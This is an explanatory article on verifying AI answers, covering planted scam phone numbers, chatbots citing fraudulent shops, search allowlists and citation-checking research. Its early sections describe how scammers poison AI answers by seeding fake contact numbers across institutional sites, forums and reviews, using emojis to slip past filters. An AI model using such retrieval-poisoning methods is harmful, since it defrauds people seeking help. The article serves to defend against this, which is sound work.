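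According to Globes' *Israeli experts uncover AI scam as tech giants deny liability*, people who ask about a cancelled flight or a branch's opening hours can get the number of a professional-sounding call centre. The staff offer the service the caller wants but charge far more than the official rate. The caller may never have seen the page the number came from, and so had no chance to notice an odd web address or clumsy design.

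The four checks barely work on a phone number. Calling it proves little, because a scammer will also answer. There is generally no public record of when someone acquired the number, and reputation services cover only numbers that people have reported. Some regulators publish phone numbers for the firms they license, but for most businesses, no authoritative directory lists all their lines. A large airline, for example, may have separate numbers for each country, for its loyalty scheme and for outside contractors.

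The best available check is probably to borrow the authority of a domain. It works like this:

1. Software finds the organisation's official domain in a directory.
2. It fetches the contact pages on that domain and extracts the phone numbers.
3. It converts those numbers and the one in the model's reply to plain digits with a country code.
4. It shows the model's number only if it matches one of the official numbers.

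Converting numbers to plain digits matters because the scammers put emojis and special characters in them to get past filters, and AI systems read the numbers anyway. The check will reject correct numbers that appear only on a branch's social media page or a partner's site. It also works only if strangers can't post on the official pages, so a help forum on the same domain shouldn't count as an official page.

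Counting how many sites give the same contact number is a poor way to check it. Ariel Simon of Vigilance told the news site Dark Reading that the operators combined university and institutional sites with forums, social networks and reviews, so a planted number can seem to have several independent sources. Taking down individual posts doesn't achieve much, because thousands of new ones appear every day, according to Globes, and cached copies continue to supply the numbers after a site deletes the originals.

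The researchers reported the problem to Google and OpenAI. Google replied that misleading AI answers were outside the scope of its reward programme for security flaws. OpenAI closed the report because the findings weren't reproducible, as models' answers vary from one query to the next. That variation is a reason for developers to check the number in every reply, since a correct number in one test is weak evidence that the next will be correct.

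Fake phone numbers can do the most harm to people who are already in trouble. Graphika's *Dial F for Fraud* describes scammers who use fake Apple Pay, Venmo and Cash App lines to target people looking for a number to report fraud. An AI summary may present one of these fake numbers as a "key contact". If an assistant can't confirm a bank's number, it can tell the user to call the one printed on their card.

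### Shops and the Podqi test

In September 2026, Podqi, a company that protects brands from counterfeiters, asked ChatGPT, Gemini and Perplexity five shopping questions about 151 brands. The questions included where to buy the brand online and whether it had regional websites. According to Clubic's *Chatbots IA*, Podqi then checked the DNS providers, redirects, security certificates and prices of the 4,437 sites the chatbots cited. Risky sites appeared in 15% of Perplexity's answers, 8% of ChatGPT's and 4% of Gemini's, and Podqi couldn't explain the differences.

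Of the 718 domains that Podqi classed as risky, 351 were fraudulent and 367 were inactive, according to Daily Pakistan's *Online Shopping through ChatGPT could lead Users to Scam Websites, study warns*. An inactive domain can't be used to cheat anyone today, but someone could buy it and open a fake shop there. Software could remove about half of the risky domains by checking that each one resolves and shows a real page. Checking DNS alone would miss some inactive sites, because Podqi also counted those that load a blank page.

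Questions about regional sites and international delivery produced a risky site in 16% of answers, compared with 6% for a plain question about where to buy. Some of the brands had no local shop, so asking about their regional sites prompted the chatbot to look for something that didn't exist. Of the risky sites in those answers, 36% had a country ending or a region's name in the domain, which made them look official.

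Podqi advises shoppers to start from a brand's main site and find the local store there. Software can do the same by reading the list of country stores on the main site and rejecting any other site that the model labels as official. It should also be able to tell users that the brand has no local store.

These rates don't describe everyday shopping. Podqi chose the brands and questions in advance, and its sample included streetwear labels that counterfeiters often copy. It used different AI models to classify the sites in different rounds of testing, which could have affected the counts. Podqi also sells protection against fake sites.

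Risky sites appeared about twice as often for small brands as for large ones. Small shops are also the hardest to verify. An honest shop that opened last month has a new domain, no reputation and no entry in any directory of official sites, and so does a fake shop that opened last month. A company register may confirm that a business exists, but it often gives no web address, and a scammer can copy a real company's registration details onto a fake site.

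A fake shop may even look better than a real one in checks of domain age and reputation. According to Tom's Guide's *ChatGPT et Gemini peuvent vous diriger vers de faux sites marchands*, the risky sites Podqi identified include domains that once belonged to real brands and that other people later bought. A domain that changes hands without lapsing can keep its old registration date, and its good reputation may outlast the sale. Page content can also mislead. TechSpot reports that ChatGPT's shopping results linked to convincing copies of the Russell & Bromley and Dunelm sites, which took orders and stole payment details but delivered nothing.

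Models don't reliably detect that a business has no history. In a test described by ConsumerAffairs, the marketing agency Fractl put an invented company among five real competitors in simulated search results. Six of nine models recommended the invented company in 94% to 100% of runs.

### Adding a warning instead of removing the link

Removing every unknown shop would also exclude honest new ones. An assistant can instead show the link with a warning and let the shopper decide. In Podqi's test, the chatbots warned the user in only 9% of the answers that included a risky site. They recommended the site as a place to shop in 57% and mentioned it without comment in 34%. ChatGPT gave a warning in 24% of its risky answers and Perplexity in 2%. When the question was simply where to buy, only one of 82 risky answers included a warning.

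A general warning can be almost useless. When Podqi asked about Birkenstock, ChatGPT warned that copies were common on cut-price marketplaces, then cited `birkenstockonsales.com`, a dead domain, as a source. A better warning appears beside the link and states what a check found, for example that the domain was registered three weeks ago and that no official source connects it to the brand. Code can write this warning from the lookup results. Podqi didn't test whether shoppers act on warnings.

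When an AI agent makes purchases, a written warning protects the buyer only if the software also holds the payment until a person approves it. Manic (2026), in *AI Shopping Agents Bought A Fake Deal 37% Of The Time*, sent nine models on 6,156 simulated Christmas shopping trips that included an obviously fake deal. Claude Opus never bought it, but the nine models overall bought it 37% of the time.

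Google responded to the Podqi test by saying that Gemini shows links to its sources so that users can verify its answers. The links help users catch an invented address, because the source won't contain it. If the answer comes from planted content, though, the source may be the scammer's own page, which will match the answer.

How strict the software should be depends on what the user is about to do and whether a directory exists. It should remove known malicious sites and dead links. For a bank's login page or phone number, it is reasonable to refuse anything that an official record doesn't confirm, because the loss from a mistake is large and such records often exist. For a small shop selling shoes, a specific warning seems fairer. Either way, the software should check the address again when the user clicks, because the domain may have changed owners.

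## Limiting which sites an assistant may search and cite

A search allowlist limits which sites' pages reach the model. Removing a bad link from a finished answer doesn't remove what the model picked up from the linked page. *Curated retrieval versus open web search in public AI information services* (Einarsson, Einarsson and colleagues, 2026) mentions a journalist who put a made-up claim on a personal web page and, within a day, saw mainstream assistants repeat it as fact. Few allowlists would have included that page.

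The filter usually works like this:

1. The developer's software sends the search service a list of permitted domains.
2. The model decides whether the user's question needs a search and, if so, writes a query.
3. The search service finds pages and removes any from domains that aren't on the list.
4. The model reads the remaining results and writes an answer with citations.

AWS's *Domain and publish date filters for Web Search on AgentCore* describes Amazon's version, in which the service also checks the raw results before returning them. It fails closed, discarding any result whose domain it can't recognise.

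As with other rules, a list of allowed sites is much weaker when it appears only in the prompt than when software enforces it. When Einarsson and colleagues put a list of trusted domains in the instructions of a public information service, the share of citations to those domains rose only from 12% to 21%.

One AWS code sample relies on the prompt to restrict searches. It serves 200 imaginary customers, each with its own approved sources, by instructing the model to include the right filters in every search. AWS warns that this isn't hard enforcement. A safer design has ordinary code attach the customer's list to each search, so the model can't leave it out.

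### Matching a page to an entry

Suppose a made-up medical society publishes treatment guidelines at `heartguide.example`. It also has a site for patients and a forum, each on its own subdomain. Somebody else owns `heartgulde.example`, with an "l" in place of the "i". Under the rules in Anthropic's *Server tools*, the result depends on how the developer writes the entry:

| Page that the search finds | Entry: `heartguide.example` | Entry: `patients.heartguide.example` | Entry: `heartguide.example/guidelines` |
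|---|---|---|---|
| `heartguide.example/guidelines/statins` | Keep | Remove | Keep |
| `patients.heartguide.example/statins` | Keep | Keep | Remove |
| `forum.heartguide.example/statins` | Keep | Remove | Remove |
| `heartgulde.example/guidelines/statins` | Remove | Remove | Remove |

Putting a parent domain on the allowlist also allows all its subdomains, including a forum the developer may not have wanted, while listing a subdomain allows only that subdomain. Software compares the characters in each address, so it always rejects a lookalike domain unless whoever compiled the list copied the lookalike's address into it by mistake.

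Developers who write their own filter should also check that a page's domain either equals the allowlist entry or ends with a full stop followed by the entry. Without the full stop, `myheartguide.example` would match the entry `heartguide.example`, because it ends with the same characters.

Allowlist entries that include a path, such as `/guidelines`, work for Anthropic's search tool but never match in its web fetch tool, which opens a page at a given address. If a developer uses the same list for both tools, the model can find a guideline in the search results but can't open it.

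OpenAI and Microsoft also include subdomains automatically. Google's and Amazon's descriptions of their filters don't give a rule for subdomains, so developers should test how those filters handle a subdomain before relying on them.

### What the main providers allow

Limits differ widely between providers, and Google alone has several. Google Cloud's *Google Search tool* covers Google's own search for agents. Its *Grounding with Parallel Web Search* and *Grounding with Exa web search* cover two outside search companies that customers can use instead.

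| | Permitted domains | Blocked domains |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | 100 | 100 |
| Anthropic | No stated number, but a long list can cause an error | The same |
| Google's search tool for agents | 20 | 2,000 |
| Google with Parallel | 200 | 200 |
| Google with Exa | 1,200 | 1,200 |
| AWS | 100 for the organisation and 100 per request | The same |

Providers also differ in how they handle requests that list both permitted and blocked domains. Anthropic rejects such requests. OpenAI's guide presents the two lists as alternatives, but its sample code sends both. In Google's tool for agents, a blocked domain stays blocked regardless of other settings. That tool also lets a developer name up to 20 pages for the model to read. It fetches each one unless its domain is blocked, so these pages can come from outside the permitted list.

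A company may want one list for everybody and shorter lists for particular tasks. AWS supports this by letting both the administrator and each request set an allowlist and a denylist. A search covers only domains that are on both allowlists, and a domain on either denylist is blocked. If the administrator allows `fda.gov`, `nih.gov` and `clinicaltrials.gov`, and a request asks for `nih.gov` and `who.int`, the search covers only `nih.gov` because the administrator hasn't allowed `who.int`.

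AWS drops `who.int` without an error message, so a developer who mistypes a domain may notice only that the search finds less. Anthropic's 2025 documentation described the same principle, but a request that conflicted with the organisation's list produced an error, which is easier to debug. Developers send OpenAI the list with each request, so a company can route requests through its own software and add the list there.

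(A search list doesn't necessarily control what an agent can contact by other means. Anthropic, for example, keeps a separate list of permitted network hosts, which its web search doesn't use.)

### How people compile the lists

The simplest way to make an allowlist is to have someone who knows the subject list the sites they trust. OpenAI's sample allowlist for a question about a diabetes drug contains PubMed, ClinicalTrials.gov, the World Health Organization and two US health agencies. This method works for narrow subjects, but the list depends on what its author knows.

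Listing types of institution takes less work than listing sites one by one. Google's option with Parallel accepts whole domain endings, so a single entry such as `.gov` or `.edu` can admit thousands of sites. But these entries can leave out obvious sources, such as the World Health Organization, which uses `who.int`, and most governments outside the United States, which don't use plain `.gov`. The right types also depend on the subject. For medical questions, *Verified Misguidance* gives government health agencies the top score of 5 and wikis and forums a 1.

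Developers can give each domain a credibility score, then set a stricter threshold for medical questions than for questions about films. To check model-written encyclopedia articles, Saeed and Razniewski (2026), in *LLMpedia*, compiled a scored list of 133 domains belonging to encyclopedias, governments, academic publishers and news agencies. Their software reads up to three of the best-scoring pages it finds on a subject. Someone still has to decide what the scores mean and update them when a site changes.

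Licensing can also decide what is on a list, because a company may only be able to use sources it has paid for. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Knowledge Is Not Free*, had GPT-4.1-mini sort 20,000 web domains by how hard they are to access:

| Kind of source | Share of domains |
|---|---|
| Open community sites, such as Wikipedia and forums | 9.52% |
| General open web, such as blogs and news sites | 71.75% |
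| Curated, official or professional sources | 13.58% |
| Paywalled or otherwise restricted sources | 5.16% |

In experiments, two small models didn't reliably give better answers when they could use more of the costly material, even on medical questions, where that material included textbooks. With one selection method, Qwen3-8B's score on a medical test fell from 84 to 79 as its budget for costly sources rose from 5 to 30.

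### A medical trial in which the list helped

Masanneck, Epping and colleagues (2025), in *Evaluating Web Retrieval–Assisted Large Language Models With and Without Whitelisting*, tested a list of just two domains, `aan.com` and `neurology.org`. They belong to the American Academy of Neurology and its journals. In March 2025, the researchers put 130 neurology questions to three Perplexity models, four times with open search and four times with the list. Two neurologists graded the answers as correct, inaccurate or wrong without knowing which system had written them, and a third settled disagreements. The shares of correct answers were:

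| | Open search | Two approved domains |
|---|---|---|
| Sonar | 60.4% | 78.1% |
| Sonar-Pro | 79.8% | 87.7% |
| Sonar-Reasoning-Pro | 81.2% | 89.0% |

OpenEvidence, an assistant for health professionals that searches only biomedical literature, got 82.5% right. Two lines of configuration were therefore enough for a general search assistant to do at least as well as a specialised one. *Evaluating the First CE‐Marked LLM‐Based Chatbot for Evidence‐Based Neurology* later gave the same questions to Prof. Valmed, a chatbot certified in Europe as a medical device. It answered over 75% correctly, significantly fewer than Sonar-Reasoning-Pro with the list.

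Sonar, the weakest model, gained the most from the list, which cut its wrong answers by about a third from 11.7% of the total. The two stronger models gave wrong answers about as often as before, so they improved mainly because inaccurate answers became correct. Sonar did worse when it cited a blog, news site or general health portal, while the reasoning model showed no significant link between its sources and its grades. Current models are much stronger than any of these three and may gain less.

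The trial was also close to the best case for an allowlist. The researchers based every question on the academy's guidelines, which the academy publishes on the approved sites. Half of the questions described a patient, so the models had to apply the guidelines and not just find a sentence, but the approved sites always covered the subject. They would cover doctors' own questions less reliably.

### A public-affairs trial in which coverage ran out

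The Icelandic study shows how gaps in the approved material affect an assistant's answers. Evrópuvefur is a University of Iceland service that answers the public's questions about the European Union. Iceland had scheduled a referendum for August 29, 2026 on whether to resume membership talks, and the service was preparing to reopen. Einarsson and colleagues generated 287 questions about the debate and had Google's Gemini models answer each one twice, once using about 670 articles that experts had written for the service and once using the open web.

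Five experts then reviewed 449 of the answers. They flagged at least one source in 65 of the 187 web answers (35%), nearly always because it was untrustworthy or irrelevant. They flagged the service's own articles far less often, and only for being out of date. A web answer's fluency and fit to the question did not indicate whether its sources were sound, so a reader would have had trouble spotting the bad ones.

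But the articles dated from 2011 to 2013, during Iceland's previous attempt to join the EU. They often lacked information on later events, and the model then replied that it couldn't answer. Open search answered far more questions. Most of the difference in quality between the two methods disappeared when the researchers set aside whether an answer addressed the question at all.

A single archive that nobody has updated for 13 years is narrower than most allowlists, so the gap in coverage was probably unusually large. The questions also didn't come from real users. Still, a list could realistically fail this way, since public bodies often have good material that they stopped maintaining when funding ran out.

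In 287 open-web answers, the model never cited RÚV, Iceland's public broadcaster and most widely used news source. Adding RÚV to an allowlist might not have helped, because an allowlist only filters results and can't add pages that the search service never found.

### How much a list leaves out

Wu and colleagues counted the domains in MS MARCO v2.1, a collection of web pages that researchers use to test search systems. The collection contains about 113.5 million segments of text from 1,035,806 domains. English Wikipedia supplies 6.17% of the segments, and the 30 largest domains supply 16.89%. The other 83% comes from about a million domains, which average roughly 91 segments each.

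Even a list of the 20,000 largest domains, 200 times as long as OpenAI permits, would cover only 72.77% of the text segments.

These figures measure the amount of text, not how many answers users would lose. Thousands of sites repeat the usual dose of a common painkiller, so a user loses nothing if the assistant can read only one good page about it. But the opening hours of a village library may appear only on one small site. Also, nobody would choose approved sites by size alone.

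The share of subjects a site covers is a slightly better measure of what users would miss if an assistant could search only that site. Saeed and Razniewski had GPT-5-mini write roughly a million encyclopedia articles from memory, choosing its own subjects by following links from one article to the next. Wikipedia covered only 56.7% of those subjects. Even on the subjects it covered, Wikipedia neither supported nor contradicted 30.5% of the model's claims, so a site that covers a subject may still lack the fact a user needs.

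The neurology results allow a rough estimate of how much coverage a list needs. Let *c* be the share of users' questions that the approved sites can answer, and assume that the assistant answers none of the others correctly. With the list, Sonar-Reasoning-Pro would be right in *c* × 89.0% of cases, compared with 81.2% for open search. The list comes out ahead only if:

*c* > 81.2 / 89.0 ≈ 0.91

So the approved sites would have to cover about 91% of the questions, or about 77% for the weaker Sonar, which gained more from the list. This calculation treats "I found nothing" as no better than a wrong answer. In medicine it is usually much better, so a hospital could reasonably accept lower coverage. A developer can measure *c* by running a few hundred real questions with and without the list and counting correct answers, wrong answers and refusals separately.

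### Bad material on approved sites

Approving a domain approves everything on it, whoever wrote it. Many respectable sites host material from outsiders, such as forums, students' personal pages and comments under news articles. Scammers in the Dark Sourcery campaign planted fake phone numbers on university and institutional sites, and a rule admitting all `.edu` domains could let such numbers through.

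Even `nih.gov`, which AWS includes in a sample list for a drug company, hosts much that the US National Institutes of Health didn't write. One of its subdomains is a huge archive of papers from outside journals, including the neurology trial, whose authors work in Düsseldorf. Approving only particular subdomains or paths can keep out some of this material if the site separates its own work from other people's.

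Approved sites can also be wrong or outdated, as the Icelandic archive was. AWS lets developers restrict results by publication date, which suits news and prices. Date limits are riskier for guidelines, because the filter removes every page without a recognised date, and an old guideline may still be current. A recent date also doesn't prove that the advice is new, since a site can republish old advice.

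### Answers that don't come from the list

When no approved site has an answer, the model may give one anyway. AWS's *Web Search* describes a model that tells the user when results don't support an answer, instead of answering from its training data. The Icelandic model often did the same. But models can't be relied on to decline at the right time, as Lee's small models showed with "None".

According to Anthropic's *Web search tool*, a search with no matches returns an empty list, while a failed search returns an error inside a response that otherwise looks successful. A program that checks only the response's overall status will miss both. The program should also check the search results and tell the user whether the approved sources had no matches or the search failed.

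The model may also answer without searching, in which case the allowlist has no effect. Anthropic explains that Claude searches for recent or changing information but answers questions about established facts directly. If someone asks about a long-established drug, the model could answer from its training data, which may include the forums that the developer excluded.

*Does the Citation Matter?* (2026) examined the AI summaries that Google shows above its results for health questions. A summary's accuracy was unrelated to how well the cited pages supported it, and summaries without citations scored about as well as those with them. One possible reason is that the model relies more on its training than on the pages it retrieves. If so, restricting the pages would change the citations more than the answers. The paper still recommends that Google prefer academic and government sites to consumer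 ones.

This is consistent with the neurology trial, where the list clearly changed the answers. Perplexity's models were weaker and the questions concerned specific guidelines, so access to the right page probably helped them more. An allowlist should help most when the model can't answer correctly without searching.

Models can also cite addresses from memory. *Characterizing Web Search by Conversational LLM Agents* (2026) found that most cited addresses came from search results, but some came from the model's training. A search filter can't block those, so the developer's software should compare every citation with the addresses the search returned and remove any that don't match.

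The citations also show only part of what the model read. In the same study, agents cited between 1.7% and 34.0% of the search results they received in everyday use, depending on the platform. OpenAI lists every address the model consulted in a separate field, which is more useful for an audit. Neither the citations nor this list establishes that an answer matches its source, so a fidelity check is still needed.

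### Whether lists favour large publishers

A list of 100 domains leaves out nearly every website. Whoever compiles it will think first of big newspapers, famous universities and national agencies. A local paper that broke a story, or a specialist who runs the best site on a rare disease, can be missing because the compilers had never heard of them. A new site can't get onto the list by being cited, because the assistant never reads sites that aren't already on it.

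Einarsson and colleagues were wary of restricting sources because choosing them can turn into editorial control. The problem is worse when a public body draws up the list. Opinion columns and partisan sites are poor evidence for factual claims, but they are a legitimate part of the debate before a referendum. As a lighter alternative, the researchers mention letting users choose which domains the assistant may draw on for a question.

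Defenders of allowlists usually reply that open search isn't neutral either. *Source Coverage and Citation Bias in LLM-based vs. Traditional Search Engines* (2025) compared six AI search engines with two traditional ones on 55,936 questions. The AI engines gave 4.3 addresses per answer on average, compared with 10 for the traditional engines, and tended to favour established sites with many references.

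The evidence on whether AI search favours larger sites is mixed, though. The same study found that the sites in AI answers were less popular on average than those in traditional results, and 37% of their domains didn't appear in the traditional results. An allowlist would remove many of those smaller sites. *Characterizing Web Search by Conversational LLM Agents* compared the domains agents cited with the results they had received, and found that the cited domains ranked higher than average. AI search may therefore retrieve less popular sites but cite the better-known ones among them.

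### The preferences of agents without a list

*Source Preference in the Wild* (Song, Park and colleagues, October 2026) gives more direct evidence that models favour certain sources. It tested 12 models on 4,822 requests to find products, hotels or academic papers on the web. The study paired items that met the same requirements but came from different sites, and rotated the order of the results so that each item appeared in every position. Every model preferred some sites and avoided others. All 12 favoured Walmart, for example, but only two favoured Target.

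The researchers then looked at pairs in which one item met one requirement fewer, counting only cases where the model chose exactly one of the two:

| Source of the worse item | Source of the better item | How often the model chose the worse item |
|---|---|---|
| Preferred | Avoided | 68% |
| Neutral | Neutral | 19% |
| Avoided | Preferred | 2% |

(These are medians across the models and subjects.)

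Part of this might reflect differences in the items that the requirements didn't capture. To test this, the researchers kept each item's title and description and swapped the sources. Every model chose the same item more often when it carried a preferred source's label. For products, the increase ranged from 19 to 65 percentage points.

Such preferences can come from training. When the researchers trained three small models on pairs in which a fictional shop had the better product 80% of the time, the models then chose that shop 70% to 75% of the time between equally good products. Missing information also contributes. If a listing gave no price, models sometimes treated a preferred shop as cheap, and adding the same price to both listings weakened the preference.

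The study supports the claim that open search already favours some sources, but not that it favours large ones. Target and Expedia are both large, and half of the models avoided Expedia. The study covered shops, hotels and papers, but not news. A model's preference against a site only makes the site less likely to be chosen, whereas an allowlist that omits it rules it out entirely.

An excluded publisher can see and challenge its omission from a published allowlist, but it can't appeal against a preference encoded in a model's weights. This advantage depends on the developer stating its criteria and answering requests to join. An assistant could also search the approved sites first and, if they have nothing, offer clearly labelled results from the wider web.

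An allowlist doesn't remove the model's preferences, because the model still chooses among the approved sites. Song and colleagues found that hiding web addresses and site names weakened those preferences. Hiding them could work well for comparing hotels, but for medical or political questions it would also hide who is making a claim, which is information the model needs to judge it.

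## Checking that a citation is suitable and says what is claimed

A search filter can't stop a model from misreporting the pages it reads, so the citations in its answer need checking too.

### From a reference to a verdict

Take the coding assistant's citation for its PDF package again. Suppose the reply says that the package "extracts tables from bank statements more accurately than its rivals", and the cited paper is called *Table Extractors Compared* (a made-up title). A full check has five steps:

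1. Resolve the reference. Software looks up the paper's DOI, a permanent code for a publication, or searches a catalogue for the title. The catalogue has the paper.
2. Match the details. The title, authors and year in the reply agree with the catalogue's entry.
3. Fetch the text. The publisher offers the paper free, so the software downloads it.
4. Find the passage. A search of the paper turns up the sentence "On clean, typed invoices, the package extracted 96% of cells correctly, against 91% for the next best tool."
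5. Judge whether the passage supports the reply. It doesn't, because the researchers tested invoices and the assistant made a claim about bank statements.

A checker that stopped after finding the passage would have marked this citation as verified. The assistant could fix the sentence by limiting it to typed invoices.

A check of a reference's details should allow some differences. *CiteAudit* (2026), a benchmark for checking scientific references, accepts a small difference in year because papers often appear as preprints before final publication. But it counts a DOI that belongs to a different work as an error. Readers can easily miss this error because the reference looks complete.

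### Scientific references that no database recognises

Software can often catch wholly invented references in the first two steps. *HalluCitation Matters* (2026) found such references in papers at three major language-technology conferences and their workshops. The number of affected papers rose from 20 in 2024 to 275 in 2025, and simply matching titles against databases was enough to detect the invented references. People find them harder to spot because most affected papers contain only a few.

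*Hallucination Detector* (2026) describes a tool that compares references with Semantic Scholar, a large catalogue of research papers. Given 100 references that experts had confirmed as fabricated, it labelled 66 as likely fakes and 28 as partial matches, and missed six. It tended to miss references that combined several kinds of deception. The set contained no genuine references, so the test can't show how often the tool wrongly flags one.

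False alarms are likely, since real references can fail to match. In *Detecting Hallucinated and Suspicious Citations* (2026), Badalova and Mayr tested five checkers on documents with invented references. The tools often gave useful early warnings, but they also misread references, relied on incomplete records, searched databases with limited coverage and returned inconsistent results.

*Testing Our Foundations* (2026), a study of computing-education papers, shows how much work it takes to confirm that a reference is hallucinated. Its candidates included 904 references that appeared to cite a venue in the field but whose titles software couldn't match to a known publication. Reviewers removed any with a credible publication record, and a second reviewer searched databases, publishers' pages and the web for the rest. The researchers called a reference hallucinated only if repeated searches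 failed and it contained details they could show were fabricated, not just a missing author or venue.

The later steps lose many genuine references. *RefVerifier* (Mocan, Angermeir and Kreitz, 2026) automated the whole chain for people who review scientific manuscripts. The software found free full text for 57.6% of references. It located the relevant passage 98% of the time when it searched only an abstract, but 68% of the time when it searched a complete paper. If both full-text rates held for the same manuscript, the software would find the right passage for only about 39% of the manuscript's references.

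In a test on eight manuscripts, 71% of RefVerifier's verdicts were correct. That figure does not separate missed errors from false alarms, and it is too low for the software to reject a paper by itself. Mocan and colleagues leave the decision to the reviewer, who gets the passage and an explanation to check.

Some wrong verdicts come from comparing too much of a sentence with the source. Suppose an author writes, "Small firms waste hours on paperwork, but this package reads typed invoices well," and cites the paper on table extractors. The paper has nothing on wasted hours, so a strict checker could reject a good citation. *Understanding before verifying* (2026) adds a stage that rewrites the sentence as the claim the source should support. The software then looks for evidence in the paper and classifies the citation.

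Medical references have the same problem. According to *Verified Misguidance*, a 2025 study by Kevin Wu, Eric Wu and colleagues found that sources did not fully support up to 90% of models' answers to medical questions.

### Good sources and faithful answers

*Verified Misguidance*, published in May 2026, measured both suitability and fidelity on a far larger scale. The researchers took 400 questions from each of 28 Stack Exchange communities, 11,200 in all, on subjects from medicine and law to bicycles. In March and April 2026 they put each question to ten search-equipped models from five companies. They then fetched the cited pages and could evaluate 761,495 citations.

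To score suitability, they built a matrix of ten subjects and six kinds of source. Each cell has a score from 1 to 5, and a score of 1 or 2 counts as a failure. Four of the ten rows look like this:

| Subject of the page | Official body | Research paper | News | Wiki or forum | Blog or social media | Company |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Medicine | 5 | 5 | 3 | 1 | 1 | 2 |
| Finance | 5 | 5 | 3 | 2 | 2 | 3 |
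| Programming | 4 | 4 | 3 | 5 | 2 | 3 |
| Everyday life | 4 | 3 | 4 | 4 | 4 | 3 |

Forums score highest for programming because developers test and correct each other's answers there. Panels of ten people with relevant expertise rated the cells for each subject, and their average was always less than two points from the researchers' score. One weakness is that the row depends on the subject of the cited page, not the subject of the question. A shop's page about vitamins would get a passing 3 if the software classed it as shopping, even if the user had asked about a disease.

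For fidelity, a model compared each citing sentence with the text of the page and chose one of five labels:

| Score | Label | What the page contains | Share of citations |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | Supported | The claim | 61.2% |
| 4 | Amplified | A weaker or narrower claim | 7.1% |
| 3 | Contradicted | The opposite of the claim | 1.1% |
| 2 | Misattributed | Related material about something else | 6.1% |
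| 1 | Fabricated | Nothing that makes the claim | 24.5% |

The researchers counted the last two as failures, which gives a fidelity failure rate of 30.6%. Oddly, they didn't count citations to pages that contradict the answer. Including those raises the rate to 31.7%, and adding the amplified ones brings it to 38.8%.

A sentence can be true even if its citation is "fabricated." Grok 4.1 correctly described the layers of an image-recognition system but cited a tutorial that didn't give those details, so a reader who followed the link couldn't have confirmed them. The details came from the system's original paper.

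Suitability failures made up 27.1% of citations. The rate was 38.3% for pages on medicine, law and finance, compared with 21.1% for other subjects. (A third score, for whether a page's purpose suited the question, failed 5.1% of citations. An advertisement cited for a simple fact is one example.)

The models that cited the most suitable sources were often the least accurate in representing what those sources said. GPT-5 had a suitability failure rate of 8.0% and a fidelity failure rate of 42.3%, while Claude Haiku 4.5's rates were 30.1% and 12.3%. GPT-5 took 41.8% of its citations from official bodies and 5.3% from blogs or social media, compared with 12.8% and 31.8% for Haiku.

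The researchers didn't test an allowlist, but one would probably reduce the suitability failures and leave most of the fidelity failures. GPT-5 chose mostly suitable sources, and its sentences still often failed to match them. A developer who checks only suitability or only fidelity will miss many failures, since 22.2% of all citations failed on fidelity alone and 19.8% on suitability alone.

Fidelity seems to vary more with the model than suitability does. Perplexity's reasoning model had a fidelity failure rate of 18.0%, against 34.1% for its standard model, while their suitability rates differed by less than two percentage points. But reasoning made little difference to either rate in xAI's two models.

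### How far to trust those figures

Part of the contrast between GPT-5 and Haiku may come from how the researchers collected the sentences. For GPT-5, they took the two sentences before each citation marker, which could include one the citation wasn't meant to support. For Haiku, they used a field called `cited_text`. In their printed example, it matches the cited fitness-app page almost word for word, including the aside "(a recipe for injury)". If the field holds the page's words and not the model's, the judge was comparing the page with itself, and Haiku's fidelity score is too good. This is an inference from the example and the field's name, but if correct, it would affect the study's main comparison.

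The researchers retrieved only 58.3% of the cited web addresses. Forums and blogs often blocked their software, so the study probably undercounts unsuitable sources of those kinds. But they also failed to retrieve many PDFs, which are often official reports or research papers, and leaving those out raises the suitability failure rate. The researchers call their rates lower bounds, which seems too confident for the suitability rate.

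GPT-4o-mini made all the judgments. On 200 fidelity samples, it agreed with the majority of three human annotators 90.5% of the time. This is good agreement, though the samples were chosen to include many of the rarer errors.

The paper also measured the share of responses that contained at least one failure of any of the three kinds, which ranged from 71.3% for Claude Haiku to 96% for Grok 4.1 with reasoning. These shares are high partly because one bad citation is enough to count a whole response, and most of the models gave more than six citations per response. The abstract presents the highest figure as the share of users who encounter a misleading citation ("up to 96%"), and the text gives that share as "up to 90%", but neither figure is a share of users.

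### Legal tools limited to legal databases

Law has an authoritative record of which cases exist and what the courts wrote. In the United States, a citation such as `276 F.3d 659` gives the volume, series and first page of a published decision. Legal publishers have built research tools that search these decisions and use them to answer questions, and some vendors marketed their tools as free of hallucinations.

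Magesh, Surani and colleagues tested that promise in *Hallucination-Free?* (2025; preprint 2024). They asked three commercial tools more than 200 questions, and counted an answer as a hallucination if it contained incorrect information or falsely said that a source supported a claim. Lexis+ AI answered 65% of the questions accurately and Westlaw's tool 42%. LawNext's *In Redo of Its Study, Stanford Finds Westlaw's AI Hallucinates* (2024) gives hallucination rates of 17% for Lexis+ AI and 33% for Westlaw's tool. Westlaw's answers were also the longest, averaging 350 words, which gave them more chances to contain an error.

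A cited case can be real and still not support the claim. According to LLRX's *“Hallucinations” by West & Lexis AI?*, Lexis+ AI described a legal rule as still valid and cited the case that had overruled it. *Legal LLM Hallucination Should Be Evaluated as Failure of Legal Warrant* (2026) argues that a checker must consider whether an authority is still in force and applies in the relevant place, court and period. A checker that compares a sentence only with the cited opinion can't tell whether a later court rejected that opinion.

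Those products are now old. Vals AI's *Alexi* (October 2025) reported an average accuracy of 80% for four newer products on 200 legal research questions, compared with 71% for lawyers. The four included ChatGPT, but neither Westlaw nor LexisNexis took part. Vals AI scored accuracy separately from whether valid authorities supported the answer.

More recent research systems still make errors when they answer from a fixed set of laws. *How Much Do Legal RAG Systems Still Hallucinate?* (Das, Abualhaija and Bianculli, 2026) tested eight combinations of search method and model on European data-protection law and a French-language civil code. Between 8.3% and 48.3% of answers contained at least one claim that the reference material didn't support. The models included GPT-5 but also much older and smaller ones, so the upper figure is weak evidence about today's best products.

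Long answers have the same effect here as in the Westlaw test. On data-protection law, one GPT-5 system made an average of 17.9 claims per answer. Only 1.5% of its claims were unsupported, but 20.1% of its answers contained at least one unsupported claim, which is the more relevant figure for a lawyer who relies on the whole answer.

Commercial legal tools also contribute to errors in court. beSpacific's *"Hallucinations" by West and Lexis AI?* (2026) describes an April 2026 decision in which a US appeals court found errors in a brief that a lawyer had prepared with Westlaw's CoCounsel.

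### Checking what lawyers file

Liu, Stammbach and Henderson (2026), in *Who Checks the Citations?*, tested whether AI agents could find citation errors in legal briefs. They took excerpts from appeal briefs filed before 2022 and planted five kinds of error in half of them. They also included 300 summaries of rulings written by models, most of them wrong. An agent running on GPT-5 could search a free database of decisions and the web:

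| Error | What a checker needs | Share that GPT-5 caught |
|---|---|---|
| No such case exists | A lookup | Over 80% |
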